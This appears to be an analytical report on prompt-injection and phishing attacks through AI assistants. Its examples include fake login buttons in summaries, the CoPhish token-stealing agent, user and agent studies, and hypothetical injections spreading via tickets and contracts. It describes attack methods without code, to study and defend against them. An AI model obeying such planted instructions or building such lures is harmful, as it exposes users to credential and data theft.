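Radware reported the attack to Microsoft on January 16, 2026 and to OpenAI on January 31. Microsoft replied that it had passed the findings to the product team. The researchers later retested both assistants and could no longer reproduce the attack on either, which they take as a sign that the companies had blocked the routes they used.

That is the most likely explanation, but Radware doesn't cite a confirmed fix from either company. A newer model might also have ignored the old wording, or the attack could have failed by chance if it only worked occasionally. Radware doesn't report how often the attack worked at first or how many times the researchers retried it.

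### A Login button that leads to a real Microsoft page

Datadog Security Labs' *CoPhish* (2025) describes an attack that needs no injection, because the attacker builds the assistant. An attacker can use a trial licence in their own Microsoft account to make a custom chatbot, or "agent", in Microsoft's Copilot Studio and publish it on a demonstration page under a genuine microsoft.com domain. They send the link to the victim by email or chat, or try to get it into search results.

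The page looks much like Microsoft's Copilot, apart from an icon that reads "Microsoft Power Platform". It asks the user to sign in and provides a "Login" button, which attackers can point at any address. In Datadog's demonstration, the button led to Microsoft's real consent screen, where the user could grant the attacker's application access to her account, as in the OAuth attack described earlier.

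If she accepts, another genuine Microsoft page shows her a numeric code to enter in the chat. This is a normal part of signing in to a Copilot Studio agent, though it looks odd. Once she enters the code, the agent receives her token. Datadog had added a step to the agent's sign-in sequence that immediately sent a copy of the token to an outside server. Microsoft's servers sent the copy, so an employer monitoring her computer would see no connection to the attacker. The agent then continued the chat normally.

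The token from Datadog's test let its holder read, change and send the user's email and edit her OneNote notebooks. The attacker could also have the agent use the token directly, for instance to search her mail and send out the results.

As in other OAuth attacks, checking the domain doesn't help the user, who has to ask why a chatbot needs permission to send email from her account. The sign-in sequence is a fixed workflow, and the language model plays no part in the deception. The attacker gains a familiar design and a Microsoft address. In *Malicious Custom GPT on chatgpt.com lures users into installing a RAT*, Zorz (2026) found criminals gaining a similar advantage by using a chatbot on ChatGPT's own site.

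#### Who remained exposed after the policy change

Microsoft lets each organisation set a policy on which permissions its staff can grant to applications. In July 2025, Microsoft introduced a default policy that stopped ordinary users from granting applications access to files in SharePoint and OneDrive. Users could still give an application registered inside their own organisation access to their email, chats, calendar and OneNote. To exploit this, an attacker first needed an account in the organisation, but by default any member's account could register an application.

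Microsoft tightened the policy soon after Datadog published its findings. Microsoft's *Upcoming Secure by Default Settings Changes for Exchange and Teams APIs* announced that applications from other companies would need an administrator's approval to reach email and Teams content. Topedia's *Microsoft-managed default app consent policy now blocks 20 additional permissions* reports that the change also covered calendars. Four groups remained exposed:

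- **Administrators who can approve applications.** The policy doesn't apply to them. An attacker with no foothold in the organisation can send such a person a link to an outside application, and that person can grant it any permission that lets an application act for a user.
- **Staff of organisations with their own consent policies.** Microsoft changed only its default, so their protection depends on what their employer chose.
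- **People who had already given consent.** Topedia notes that they can keep using the applications they approved. The change therefore wouldn't by itself cut off a malicious application that someone had approved earlier.
- **Ordinary users with OneNote notebooks.** Datadog expected that they could still grant access to their notes. A further extension that Microsoft announced in 2026 lists contacts, people and tasks, but not OneNote.

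Attacks on administrators are the most serious, because administrators can grant the widest access and the attacker needs no account inside the organisation. Datadog advises employers to write a stricter policy, stop ordinary users from registering applications and watch the logs for new agents or altered sign-in sequences. However, in a follow-up, Datadog Security Labs found that Copilot Studio was not consistently logging two of four kinds of change.

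### A flaw in the assistant or ordinary phishing?

A company that receives one of these reports has to decide whether its product is at fault or whether the attacker has only tricked a user. On February 4, 2026, Bugcrowd told Radware that its report to OpenAI was "Not Applicable". According to Bugcrowd, OpenAI said Radware hadn't demonstrated how the attack differed from other ways of persuading a victim to process or open a malicious file.

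Radware replied that in this attack the victim starts the conversation, is waiting for the answer, and receives the link from a system she already trusts. It added that the assistant can use her current task and other context to make the lure more convincing. Radware received no further response. OpenAI's reasoning is publicly known only from Radware's account of Bugcrowd's message.

One way to test the two arguments is to take the assistant away and see what the attacker has left.

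| Attack | What the attacker could do without the assistant | What the attacker would lose |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Logue's login button | Send a link to a fake login page | The emails inside the link |
| Radware's fake shop | Send a fake Amazon page | The match with the user's request, and the assistant's apparent backing |
| Radware's leaking file | Send a malicious file | The personal details from the assistant's memory and connected accounts |
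| Datadog's CoPhish | Send a link to the same consent screen | The Copilot-style page on a Microsoft domain |

OpenAI's argument is reasonable for the fake shop, because the user has to download a file, open it and type in her card number, and criminals have long sent people fake shops without an assistant's help. But the argument fails for the leaking file. A web page emailed by a stranger can't read the user's ChatGPT memory. The assistant collected the details and put them in the file without her asking, and she had no way of knowing they were there.

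Radware's reply relies mainly on the lure being more persuasive, which its demonstrations didn't measure. Victims of ordinary fraud also commonly start the interaction themselves, for example by searching for a shop and clicking on a fake one. The point about context is stronger, because one set of instructions could produce a different page for each user. Radware's best evidence is that the assistant gathered private data without permission, but Radware's summary of the reply mentions context only as a way to improve the lure. Radware says it sent OpenAI "the same general attack class", which doesn't establish how clearly its report to OpenAI demonstrated the leak.

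OpenAI's other statements support treating the leak as a flaw. In December 2025, it fixed an attack that stole data from ChatGPT without a click, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*. Zvika Babo, who co-wrote Radware's article, had also reported that attack through Bugcrowd. In March 2026, OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* set out the principle that sensitive information shouldn't leave silently or without safeguards. The leaking file broke that principle by sending the data as soon as the user opened it.

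Two weeks later, OpenAI (2026) launched a bounty programme that accepts reports of outside text hijacking an agent and making it leak a user's sensitive information, provided the attack works at least 50% of the time. Radware's leaking file resembles this kind of attack, but without a success rate it is impossible to say whether it would have qualified.

#### Where Microsoft and Google draw the line

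Microsoft bases its severity ratings for AI systems on the outcome. In the November 2024 version, a prompt injection that steals another user's data is "Critical" if it needs no clicks and "Important" if it needs one or more. If the attacker can only influence what the assistant writes, Microsoft treats the attack as a content issue and assesses it separately. Logue's button and Radware's leaking file both count as data theft under these rules. The fake shop is harder to classify because the assistant writes a false page but the user supplies the data herself.

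Microsoft has gone beyond a strict reading of those rules. Its advisory on the flaw Permiso found covers phishing messages as well as leaked data. It also patched several Copilot flaws under the catalogue number CVE-2026-24299. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* lists data leaks through Copilot's HTML preview among them. Microsoft described CoPhish as social engineering (manipulating people) but acknowledged the report and said it would work on the problem, according to TechRadar's *Experts warn Microsoft Copilot Studio agents are being hijacked*.

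Google used the same label when it declined to stop Gemini from following instructions written in invisible characters. It told the security company FireTail, which had reported the problem, that the attack "can only result in social engineering", according to BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*. But Google's bounty rules for AI products do cover some phishing. According to SecurityWeek, a report can qualify if an attacker can plant lasting HTML on a Google-branded site where other users will see it, the page doesn't warn that a user wrote the content, and the attack is convincing.

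Under that rule, a trusted site contributes to the deception when it displays an outsider's content as its own. The same reasoning applies to CoPhish. Criminals who abuse Microsoft's real sign-in process in other ways often have to register imitation domains, which filters can be updated to block. Microsoft lists several such domains from one campaign. With Copilot Studio, the attacker gets a genuine Microsoft domain that employers are unlikely to block. The consent trick is ordinary phishing, but Microsoft controls how clearly the page shows that a stranger built the agent.

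Even when an attacker relies on social engineering to get the click, the company that makes the assistant may be able to stop the attack. Microsoft stopped Logue's attack by removing links from diagrams, which didn't require users to be more careful.

The need for a click still affects how serious a flaw is, but people disagree about how much. In June 2026, the security company Varonis described a Copilot attack that stole emails, security codes and files after one click. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Varonis called the flaw critical, while Microsoft rated it medium, at 6.5 out of 10, partly because the user had to click. If nearly everyone would click, that requirement offers little protection. Logue, Radware and Datadog didn't test their controls on unsuspecting users, so their work can't show how much the need for a click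 should lower a flaw's severity rating.

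## Experiments on whether people and agents notice the deception

No known experiment tests whether people trust a lure more when an assistant repeats it, which is the form of trust transfer that matters most for fake login buttons. The available experiments measured related behaviour, such as whether people notice a manipulated answer or follow a chatbot's bad advice. To test it directly, researchers could put a false security alert in an email and the same alert in an AI summary of that email, show each version to people who don't know about the test, and count the clicks.

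### The missing comparison

Several writers have predicted that people could be fooled, but none of them measured it. Greshake and colleagues conjectured this in 2023, and Ahmeti had the same impression of his Copilot screenshots. eSecurity Planet's *AI Email Summaries Create a New Phishing Attack Surface* suggests that people who have learned to distrust suspicious emails may still trust a notice from their employer's assistant.

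The prediction is plausible, but there are reasons to doubt it. People seldom click on links in AI summaries. *Investigating Click Behaviors On Google Search Result Pages* (2026) used a month of browsing data from a panel of 900 people in the United States. When Google showed them an AI Overview, its AI-written summary above the search results, they clicked on a cited source in only about 1% of visits. This figure suggests that many people read a summary and move on, but it isn't an estimate for fake login buttons, because an urgent alert gives people more reason to click than a citation does. A login button is also unusual in a summary, which could make some users suspicious.

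Researchers could feasibly test whether people click on a fake alert more often in an AI assistant's summary than in an email. BIFOLD's *AI Goes Phishing* describes a field experiment in which researchers tested phishing emails on about 7,700 people and found AI-generated ones three times as effective as generic ones. That experiment covered only emails, but a comparison with summaries could need fewer people. If 10% of people would click on the alert in an email and 15% in a summary, researchers would have an 80% chance of detecting the difference with about 700 people in each group. They could also add a group that sees the summary with a provenance label, and count how many people in each group then type a password.

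### Nine tasks with a compromised agent

*Are You Sure?*, from February 2026, is the largest study of how people respond to a compromised assistant. Its researchers built HAT-Lab (Human-Agent Trust Laboratory), a platform on which people carry out realistic tasks with an AI agent. They recruited participants through Prolific, a website that pays people to take part in studies, and analysed results from 303 after excluding 26 for rushing, ignoring instructions or giving poor answers.

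Each participant did three of nine tasks in a session of about 40 minutes. Every task included an attack. In advance tests with GPT-4o, the model used in the study, the attacks worked 98.9% of the time, so almost every participant should have received a manipulated result.

| The participant's task | What the compromised agent did |
| --- | --- |
| Write cover letters | Spelled "University" as "Universität" |
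| Choose the best job candidate | Favoured a candidate whose CV contained hidden instructions |
| Write a medical report | Exaggerated a patient's depression score |
| Assess a candidate's code | Gave a flawed assessment because of a comment in the code |
| Answer a question with sources | Turned off its web search and made up citations |
| Get advice on adding a software package | Recommended a malicious package |
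| Book a medical appointment and a flight | Put private health details in the flight booking |
| Review and answer emails | Sent personal data to the attacker and deleted the evidence |
| Compare transport options | Added $10 to a competitor's fare |

Each participant also saw one of three kinds of warning:

- **A static disclaimer** appeared once, at the start of the experiment.
- **A persistent reminder** placed an icon and a short warning beside every response from the agent.
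- **An interactive alert** interrupted the participant when the agent produced suspicious output, and stayed until they acknowledged it.

The researchers asked participants whether they had noticed anything "unusual or questionable" in the agent's output, and counted both "Yes" and "Unsure" as noticing. Participants who gave either answer then had to describe the problem, and a correct description of the attack counted as accurate identification.

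The noticing rate was 8.6% with the static disclaimer, 20.0% with the persistent reminder and 25.0% with the interactive alert. Accurate identification was rarer, at 2.7% with the disclaimer and 17.2% with the alert. Only 24% of participants who received the disclaimer confirmed having seen it.

The alert helped more in some tasks than in others. Compared with the disclaimer, it raised the share of people who noticed the deception from 6.3% to 40% for the cover letters and from 9.8% to 50% for the web search, but only from 7.9% to 15% for the transport comparison and from 9.3% to 15% for the emails. The researchers attribute this to interruptions helping when people can easily check the output. A strange spelling is easy to see, but people need to know the real fare to spot an extra $10. In the email task, the agent had also deleted the evidence.

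A user would easily see a fake login notice but could only partly check it. She can look at the link's address, but she can't tell from the summary whether an unknown device really signed in to her account.

#### Warnings that made people more trusting

Participants who missed the attack often said afterwards that they trusted AI systems more than before, especially if they had seen the persistent reminder or the interactive alert. Some said the warnings made them feel safer, apparently because they took a visible warning as a sign that the system was protecting them.

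Their ratings of the experience follow the same pattern. Among people who missed the attack, the average pleasantness rating was 4.12 out of 5 with the disclaimer, 4.30 with the reminder and 4.59 with the alert. Among people who noticed it, the average stayed between 3.86 and 3.96.

This is a concern for anyone who plans to put warnings beside AI summaries, because the people who most need the warnings may come away more confident. The study measured the trust people reported at the end of one session, so it doesn't show that they became less careful. It also had no group without a warning, so some of the increase in trust may come from spending 40 minutes with an agent that seemed to work well.

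#### The results for experts

The 119 participants who worked in IT noticed attacks less often than the others under every kind of warning. Their rate was 6.8% against 9.6% with the disclaimer, 18.4% against 21.5% with the reminder, and 22.2% against 26.5% with the alert. The researchers call this the "Expert's Paradox". They suggest that experts concentrate on the quality of the agent's output and take how it works for granted.

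The evidence for a paradox is thin. The published rates imply that IT professionals noticed something in 44 of 357 tasks (12%) and the other participants in 84 of 552 (15%). The paper gives no significance test for this gap, and a gap this large would occur by chance more than one time in five if the two groups were equally observant. The groups also did different mixes of tasks, because the researchers gave the medical and coding tasks to people with relevant backgrounds.

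In the coding tasks, none of the IT professionals noticed the malicious package, compared with 8.1% of the other participants. For the flawed code assessment, the figures were 9.1% and 13.5%. But 8.1% and 13.5% are only three and five people out of 37, so a few different answers would have closed either gap. The results show only that working in IT gave people no visible protection.

Participants with a master's degree or doctorate also noticed the deception less often than those with less education (4.6% versus 10.7%). This difference was statistically significant, although the uneven allocation of tasks may have affected it too.

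#### What the percentages count

The study's summary says that only 8.6% of participants perceived the attacks. That figure covers only the people who saw the static disclaimer, and it seems to be a share of tasks, not of people. The group had 183 people, and no whole number of them comes to 8.6%, but 47 of their 549 tasks does. Elsewhere the paper counts 85 of all 303 participants, or 28%, as having perceived an attack, which presumably means at least one of their three. So most people missed every attack, but the share who noticed at least one was about three times the 8.6% given in the summary.

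The group sizes are also inconsistent. According to the description of the design, the researchers randomly assigned 101 people to the disclaimer, 103 to the reminder and 99 to the alert, but in the results the groups have 183, 60 and 60 people. Both sets add up to 303, and the paper doesn't explain the change. The comparison between warnings is fair only if people were assigned to them at random. If the researchers regrouped people later, part of the rise from 8.6% to 25.0% could come from differences between the people in each group.

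The study also had no attack-free control, so it is unknown how many people would have called an honest agent's output unusual. AI output often contains oddities, and a dialog box about suspicious output encourages people to answer "Unsure", so some of the noticing may be false alarms. The rates for accurate identification are more informative because people had to describe what had gone wrong.

Another problem is that the questionnaires may have raised the detection rates. The questionnaire for each task asked what participants had noticed, then described the manipulation and asked how serious it was. If participants filled it in after each task, they began the next one knowing that the agent might be compromised. The paper is unclear about when they filled it in.

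#### How far this is from a login button

None of the nine tasks involved a fake login button. The closest task used the malicious software package, whose name imitated that of a real project. A developer who takes the agent's advice installs the attacker's code, much as a user who clicks on a fake button opens the attacker's page. The paper reports whether participants noticed something wrong, but not how many would have installed the package.

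People might notice a fake login button more often than these attacks, because it stands out more than an inflated fare and prompts them to act. The study can't show whether this is true, and people who find a login request strange might still comply with it.

### People who followed advice they distrusted

Lit, Crowder and colleagues (2025) measured compliance directly in *I know it's not right, but that's what it said to do*. They told 15 people, none of whom worked in cybersecurity, that they would be testing a new cybersecurity chatbot. The participants imagined that they had started a remote job and had to set up a work laptop, and they changed real settings on a simulated Windows computer.

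The chatbot gave sound advice on the first three tasks. For the last two, the researchers secretly swapped in a model they had trained to give harmful advice. Depending on the task, it recommended using a password of three or four letters, opening risky ports in the firewall, running several antivirus programs at once, leaving the drive unencrypted, or turning off the automatic screen lock. It also gave reasons for this advice, for example that long passwords were out of date.

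Eight of the 15 people followed all of the bad advice and four followed some of it. Each person received two pieces of bad advice, so these numbers imply that 20 of the 30 pieces were followed, but the paper elsewhere gives a total of 16. Both totals are more than half.

Participants often followed the bad chatbot's instructions despite their doubts. The researchers classified them as distrusting it in 17 task ratings and trusting it in 11. One participant said they wouldn't trust a chatbot to help the average person set up a computer securely, but had opened the firewall ports the bad chatbot suggested. Another had little confidence in the firewall instructions but followed them because they had no other knowledge to rely on. The noticing rates in HAT-Lab therefore don't measure how often people behave safely.

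People's prior knowledge affected which advice they accepted. Most rejected the advice to turn off the screen lock because they could see the risk. They more readily accepted the advice to run two antivirus programs, which sounds like extra protection. People may also readily accept a false alert about an unfamiliar sign-in, since checking one's account after a suspicious login is normally good advice.

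People also tended to trust the chatbot more when it correctly told them where to find a Windows setting, even if its advice about the setting was bad. An accurate summary above a false notice might have a similar effect, although Lit and colleagues didn't test summaries.

The experiment made it easy to comply. The participants had no internet access, so they couldn't look anything up. The written tasks told them to act on the chatbot's advice, they knew the researchers were observing them, and the computer wasn't their own. By contrast, an employee who sees a login button in a summary can ignore it and carry on working. Fifteen participants are also too few to estimate reliably how many people in general would comply.

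Lit and colleagues suggest that people may be better prepared for phishing than for a malicious chatbot, because training against phishing is so common. This bears on trust transfer, but they did not compare the chatbot with a phishing email.

Some people protect themselves by giving false answers. In *Malicious LLM-Based Conversational AI Makes Users Reveal Personal Information* (2025), participants talked to chatbots designed to extract personal details. Participants reported giving less fake information to a chatbot with a "reciprocal" strategy than to other malicious versions. The reciprocal chatbot collected less data, but more of it was true. An experiment on fake login pages would also have to check whether people typed their real passwords.

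### An assistant that is always wrong

*Do People Trust AI Assistants Even When They Are Consistently Wrong?* (Jones, Wong and colleagues, November 2026) reports four experiments on whether people stop listening to an assistant that keeps misleading them. Participants answered 30 two-choice questions about physics, probability, logic and general facts. They then discussed five of the questions with an AI advisor, which argued for the answer the researchers had assigned to it.

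In the first four conversations, the advisor established a track record by being right every time for some participants and wrong every time for others. In the fifth, it disagreed with every participant, and the researchers recorded who switched to its answer.

When participants learned the correct answer after each conversation, 95% switched to the advisor's answer if the advisor had always been right, and 61% did if it had always been wrong. Without this feedback, the advisor's track record made no difference (90% and 89% switched).

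Participants in those experiments had been unsure of their answer to the fifth question, so changing their minds was easy. In the third experiment, with 420 students, the researchers chose a question that each student had answered correctly and with great confidence. For about half of the students, they also replaced the conversation with a single line that named an answer as the correct one and gave no reason.

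| How the AI gave its advice | Switched after it had always been right | Switched after it had always been wrong |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Conversation, with feedback | 67% | 21% |
| Conversation, without feedback | 38% | 48% |
| One line, with feedback | 25% | 6% |
| One line, without feedback | 19% | 16% |

The difference between 38% and 48% was not statistically significant. Overall, 42% of people switched after a conversation and 17% after a single line.

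The single line is closer than a conversation to a notice in a summary, because the user reads it and decides without any discussion. Persuasion rates from conversations shouldn't be applied to a summary button. Even so, the researchers estimated that only about 3% would have switched by chance, so a bare line from an AI led a noticeable minority to abandon a correct answer they were almost sure of. A security notice also gives a reason, and the user probably has no firm belief about who has signed in to her account. On the other hand, people know that a login page can be dangerous, whereas a wrong quiz answer does no harm.

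A suspicious user might also ask the assistant whether the notice is real. If the attacker's instructions still influence the assistant, it could argue that the notice is real, and the exchange would become more like the conversations in the experiment.

The finding about feedback applies more directly. Someone who types her password into a fake page may not learn that it was fake, particularly if the page then redirects her to the real service, so she would have no reason to trust the assistant less before the next false notice.

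In Jones and colleagues' fourth experiment, AI advisors persuaded people in 83% of conversations and human advisors in 65%. This resembles the missing comparison between a summary and an email, but each kind of advisor wrote its own arguments, and the AI's messages were typically about four times as long. The result therefore shows how well each argued. To measure trust transfer, researchers would have to give people the same words from different sources.

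### An app recommended by a chat partner

In *Love, Lies, and Language Models*, Gressel, Pankajakshan and colleagues (2025) came closer to testing whether people would click a fake button, because they asked people to install something. They studied romance-baiting scams, in which criminals build a relationship with someone over weeks of text messages before persuading them to invest in a fraud.

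In one experiment, 22 people chatted on WhatsApp for a week with a person and an AI agent, believing that both were people. The agent made small typing errors, waited before replying and denied being an AI if asked. On the seventh day, each partner tried to persuade the participant to install a harmless app. The AI persuaded 46% of participants (ten people) and the human partner persuaded 18% (four people).

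The participants thought they were responding to a friendly person who had paid attention to them for a week, so the result doesn't measure trust in AI assistants. They also sent 70% to 80% of their messages to the AI, and several described it as a good listener. A button in a summary appears without any such relationship.

The requests also differed, since the AI recommended a productivity app and the human partner a puzzle app, each with its own pretext. Some people may have had more use for the productivity app. The experiment had 22 participants, and the difference between the partners was six people. Still, it shows that people will install software because a language model suggested it in a chat, at least when they think the model is a person.

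### When the agent does the clicking

Some assistants now browse the web for users, clicking buttons and filling in forms. If such an agent encounters a fake login prompt, the user may never see it, so the attack has to deceive only the agent.

In August 2026, Guo, Zhang and colleagues tested whether agents notice fake login buttons in *LoginTrap*. They copied 80 real web pages in areas such as travel and shopping, and added a pop-up to each copy. The pop-up presented logging in as necessary to continue, and had a login button and a close button. The login button led to a form that the researchers controlled. They then gave agents made-up personal data and 1,175 ordinary tasks on these pages, such as finding or comparing information.

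The study used two main measures:

- **The login entry rate** is the share of tasks in which the agent clicks on the fake login button.
- **The attack success rate** is the share of tasks in which the agent clicks on the button and then also types sensitive information into the fake form.

Across four language models, agents clicked the fake login button in an average of 93% of tasks (the login entry rate) and went on to enter private data in 86% (the attack success rate). In the 7% of tasks where they clicked but entered no private data, Guo and colleagues recorded agents leaving the form incomplete, stopping early or returning to the original task. Each agent was limited to five steps, so some may have run out of steps.

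The four models were GPT-4o, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Sonnet 4 and DeepSeek-V3.2. All are older than the leading models of December 2026, which may behave differently. The researchers also ran GPT-4o in three browsing programs. Depending on the program, it clicked the login button in 84% to 94% of tasks and entered private data in 68% to 89% (79% on average). The researchers suggest that a program that plans its steps and checks its progress may make the attack more successful, because once the agent has accepted the login as part of the task, the program helps it finish.

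These rates are high partly because the researchers selected effective wording. A language model wrote a message to suit each page, without knowing what task the agent would have. Two other copies of a model then tested the message, one with a reminder to avoid suspicious instructions. The process accepted the message if both copies chose the login button, and otherwise revised and retested it. An attacker could do the same, so the method is realistic, but 93% doesn't describe how agents respond to login pop-ups in general.

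Comparing the agents' 93% with the 8.6% from HAT-Lab would also be a misleading way to judge whether agents are about as gullible as people, because the first figure measures clicks on a login button and the second measures tasks in which people reported something unusual. Guo and colleagues didn't show their pop-ups to people.

The agents tested so far were deceived far more often by buttons than by text links. *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025) compared the two in 35 matched pairs of injections on one test website, using three models. GPT-OSS-120B and Claude 3.7 Sonnet each fell for 46% of the buttons and 6% of the links. For Gemini 2.5 Flash, the rates were 66% and 9%. If these results hold more widely, an application that displays an untrusted link as a button makes it more dangerous to any agent that reads the page. Researchers could run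 the same test on people with two versions of an AI summary, one containing a button and the other a text link.

An agent can give away only the information it has. LoginTrap supplied the personal data at the start, but a real agent may not have the password for the site it is visiting. It would then have to ask the user, who would hear from her own assistant that the task requires a login. She would be in much the same position as someone reading a false notice in a summary, except that the agent would be asking for the password to finish a job she had given it.

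## How one ticket or contract can reach a whole organisation

In the attacks described so far, one person asked for one summary. Many organisations have *summarising pipelines*, which automatically feed documents, tickets or messages to a model and pass its summaries to staff or other systems. If a false notice gets into one of these summaries, it can reach people who have never opened the original document and don't know an outsider wrote it.

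Researchers have demonstrated several steps of such an attack separately, but no known demonstration shows a fake login button spreading through a whole organisation. The ticket and contract examples in this section are invented to show how the steps could fit together.

### A ticket that any customer can file

Suppose a software company lets customers report problems through a web form. An attacker files a ticket about a failed data export. Most of it is an ordinary complaint, but the attacker also includes an instruction for any assistant that summarises the ticket to add a login link and a notice that the reader's session has expired.

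1. The helpdesk program creates a record from the form and marks it as coming from a customer. The attacker needs no account. Zenity Labs' *Prompt Mines*, which examines an assistant made by Salesforce, points out that companies often put such forms on public websites without requiring a login.
2. A support agent reads an AI summary of the ticket. She sees the false notice, but the customer's name is on the same screen, so she has some chance of connecting the two.
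3. She passes the problem to the engineers, and the helpdesk program copies the ticket into their tracker. The new record may name the support agent, or the copying program, as its author.
4. An engineer asks her assistant to summarise the issues assigned to her. The notice now appears below a list of several issues, and nothing connects it to this one.
5. At the end of the week, a model turns the team's issues into a report for managers, who may not even have access to the helpdesk.

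The ticket can lose its "external" label at step 3. A helpdesk program typically keeps the customer's name in a separate field, and the copy may carry over only the text. Even if the label is copied, the summary at step 4 can drop it, because the model combines text from several records and isn't required to mark which record each sentence came from. To preserve the label, the company would have to copy it along with the text and make the summary display it.

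Some companies automatically copy outside messages into their internal systems. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes automatic copying from Zendesk, a helpdesk program, into Jira, which development teams use to track work. SecurityWeek reports that Zenity found hundreds of email systems that open Jira tickets automatically. Neither source tests how often the new ticket still shows that an outsider wrote it.

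### Attacks on real ticket and customer-record systems

Researchers have attacked at least five products of this kind. *PoC Attack Targeting Atlassian's Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Waizel, Attiya and Bamberger, 2025) describes an attack on Jira Service Management, which handles customer requests. The security company Noma attacked Salesforce's Agentforce (The Hacker News, 2025), and AppOmni attacked ServiceNow, a platform for handling IT requests. Zenity attacked Einstein, another Salesforce assistant, and Cursor, a programming tool that developers can connect to Jira.

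| Product | Where the attacker's text was | What the attack did | Did staff see a fake link or button? |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Jira Service Management | A customer's support ticket | Copied internal data into the attacker's ticket | No |
| Salesforce Agentforce | A public web form for sales enquiries | Sent customer records to a domain the attacker could buy | No |
| ServiceNow | A ticket from a user with few permissions | Copied a restricted ticket into the attacker's own | No |
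| Salesforce Einstein | Customer support cases | Gave a false answer and overwrote customers' contact details | No |
| Cursor connected to Jira | A Jira ticket | Leaked a secret from the developer's code | No |

These attacks mostly aimed to steal or change data. They show that text from an outsider or a junior user can take control of an assistant that works with a more senior employee's permissions. In two of them, the assistant also wrote text into a ticket that someone else could read. An attack that can write stolen data into a ticket could probably write a link there too, but the product might filter links or display them differently, and none of the researchers tested this.

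In the ServiceNow attack, AppOmni researcher Aaron Costello created a user who could file tickets but couldn't read anyone else's. As that user, he filed a ticket instructing any agent that read it to copy the description of a restricted ticket into his own ticket. When an administrator had an agent process the ticket, that agent called on a second one that could edit records. Both agents worked with the administrator's permissions, not those of the user who filed the ticket, and ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout.

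In other tests, Costello got agents to give a malicious user an administrator's role and to send emails containing data from other records. Costello used the emails only to get data out, but an attacker might use them to send staff a phishing link from the company's own ServiceNow system.

Einstein was harder to attack because Salesforce had designed it to display search results without the model reading them first. But the results stayed in the conversation, and the model read them when the employee asked a follow-up question. Zenity's researchers had to split their instructions across four support cases, because the model received only each case's subject line, which was limited to 255 characters. Einstein displayed only the first three cases it found, and the planted ones were further down the list, so the employee did not see the text that was about to affect the answer she received.

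#### The fake link that Cato described

Waizel and colleagues at Cato Networks also describe an attack that uses a deceptive link, but they didn't carry it out. An attacker takes over the email account of a partner company and submits a feature request containing hidden instructions. A product manager answers it with an AI template, which triggers the instructions. The assistant then comments on every open Jira issue, announcing maintenance on a page in Confluence, the company's internal document system, and linking to a fake copy of that page. The next day, a tester clicks the link, sees nothing useful and closes the page, while malware installs itself in the background.

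The demonstrated Jira attack supports the first half of this scenario, in which outside text gets an assistant to write something into Jira. It doesn't show that the assistant would comment on hundreds of issues without anyone noticing, or that opening the page would be enough to install malware. Waizel and colleagues also assume that most users would click the link. They didn't test this on anyone, though they may be right, since the comment would appear in a work tool and concern a familiar system.

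#### How the companies responded

The vendors disagreed about what needed fixing. ServiceNow updated its documentation and told AppOmni that the agents had behaved as intended. Salesforce told Zenity that it already knew about the Einstein problem but gave no date for a fix. After Noma's report, Salesforce began blocking its agents from sending output to web addresses outside an approved list.

That rule should also stop many fake login links, although it wouldn't stop a phone number. But the list has to be kept up to date. Noma's attack got past an existing security rule by using a domain that Salesforce still trusted but no longer owned, which anyone could buy for about $5.

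### A supplier's contract

Suppose a supplier emails a 60-page contract to a company's purchasing department. Someone at the supplier, or an attacker who has broken into the supplier's mailbox, has hidden instructions in an annex. The instructions tell any assistant to end its summary with a notice that one schedule is confidential and a sign-in button for viewing it.

The buyer saves the file in the company's contract system, which produces three summaries. The legal team gets a list of unusual clauses, the finance team gets the payment terms, and senior management gets a paragraph on cost and risk. The lawyers will probably also read the contract, but finance and management may rely on their summaries. A request to sign in wouldn't surprise them, because companies often restrict access to contracts.

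The mail program may have marked the supplier's email as external, but that warning doesn't move with the file. The contract system lists the buyer as the person who uploaded it. The summaries use the company's own template, and when a finance manager pastes one into a request for approval, the request has her name on it. By the time the finance director sees the button, it seems to come from a colleague.

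The lawyers are the most likely to notice something wrong, but they won't see the instructions in the contract if the text is white. Their own summary may also lack the fake button, because each team's summary comes from a separate request. The same injected text can work with one request and fail with another, as it did in the three versions of Copilot that Permiso compared.

A false notice in a contract summary can also cause harm without a button, because the finance team uses the summary to decide whom to pay. SecurityWeek describes a demonstration in which Zenity got Gemini to give a user the attacker's bank account details.

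#### A fake login in a legal assistant

The first part of this attack has worked on a real product. In December 2025, PromptArmor attacked Vincent AI, vLex's legal research assistant, using text hidden in an uploaded document. According to the law firm Jones Walker, the researchers disguised the text as a witness quotation. When the user asked Vincent for the document's direct quotations, a fake vLex login screen appeared over the chat, and anything the user typed into it would have gone to the attacker.

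This demonstration is the closest to the contract example, because a legal professional could have seen a fake login screen while doing routine work on someone else's document. The request for quotations may have helped the attack, since an assistant that quotes a document accurately will also reproduce what an attacker has put in it. The demonstration involves only one reader and doesn't show the login screen remaining in a summary that she saves or forwards. PromptArmor's *CaseBreak* says vLex has fixed the flaws.

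People outside an organisation have planted instructions for AI systems in legal documents. Thomson Reuters describes a Connecticut case, *Elliott v. New York Bariatric Group, LLC*, in which a person without a lawyer filed a document containing such instructions in tiny white text. Each side in a lawsuit has to read what the other files, so a law firm can't protect itself by accepting documents only from people it trusts.

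### Four ways one document can affect more people

**Many people read the same source.** The attacker writes the instructions once, and they can work each time someone asks an assistant for a summary. Colleagues may also use different assistants, or different versions of one assistant, so a product that resists the attack protects only its own users.

**An application stores a summary and shows it repeatedly.** Storing a summary avoids the cost of running the model for each reader. If the injection worked when the model wrote the summary, every later reader sees the fake button, and deleting the original document may not delete the summary. The demonstrations on ticket systems don't cover this case. The nearest evidence is from the Morris II experiments, described below, in which assistants stored a malicious email and reused it when writing later messages.

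**People and programs copy summaries into other systems.** Once a model has written the false notice into a summary, the notice is ordinary visible text in an internal document. A second model can repeat it by summarising that document accurately. *Trading Agents or Market Crashers?* (2026), which studies AI agents that trade shares, calls this propagation without compromise. It contrasts this with infection, in which each agent that receives the attacker's instructions passes them on. Defences on individual agents deal only with infection.

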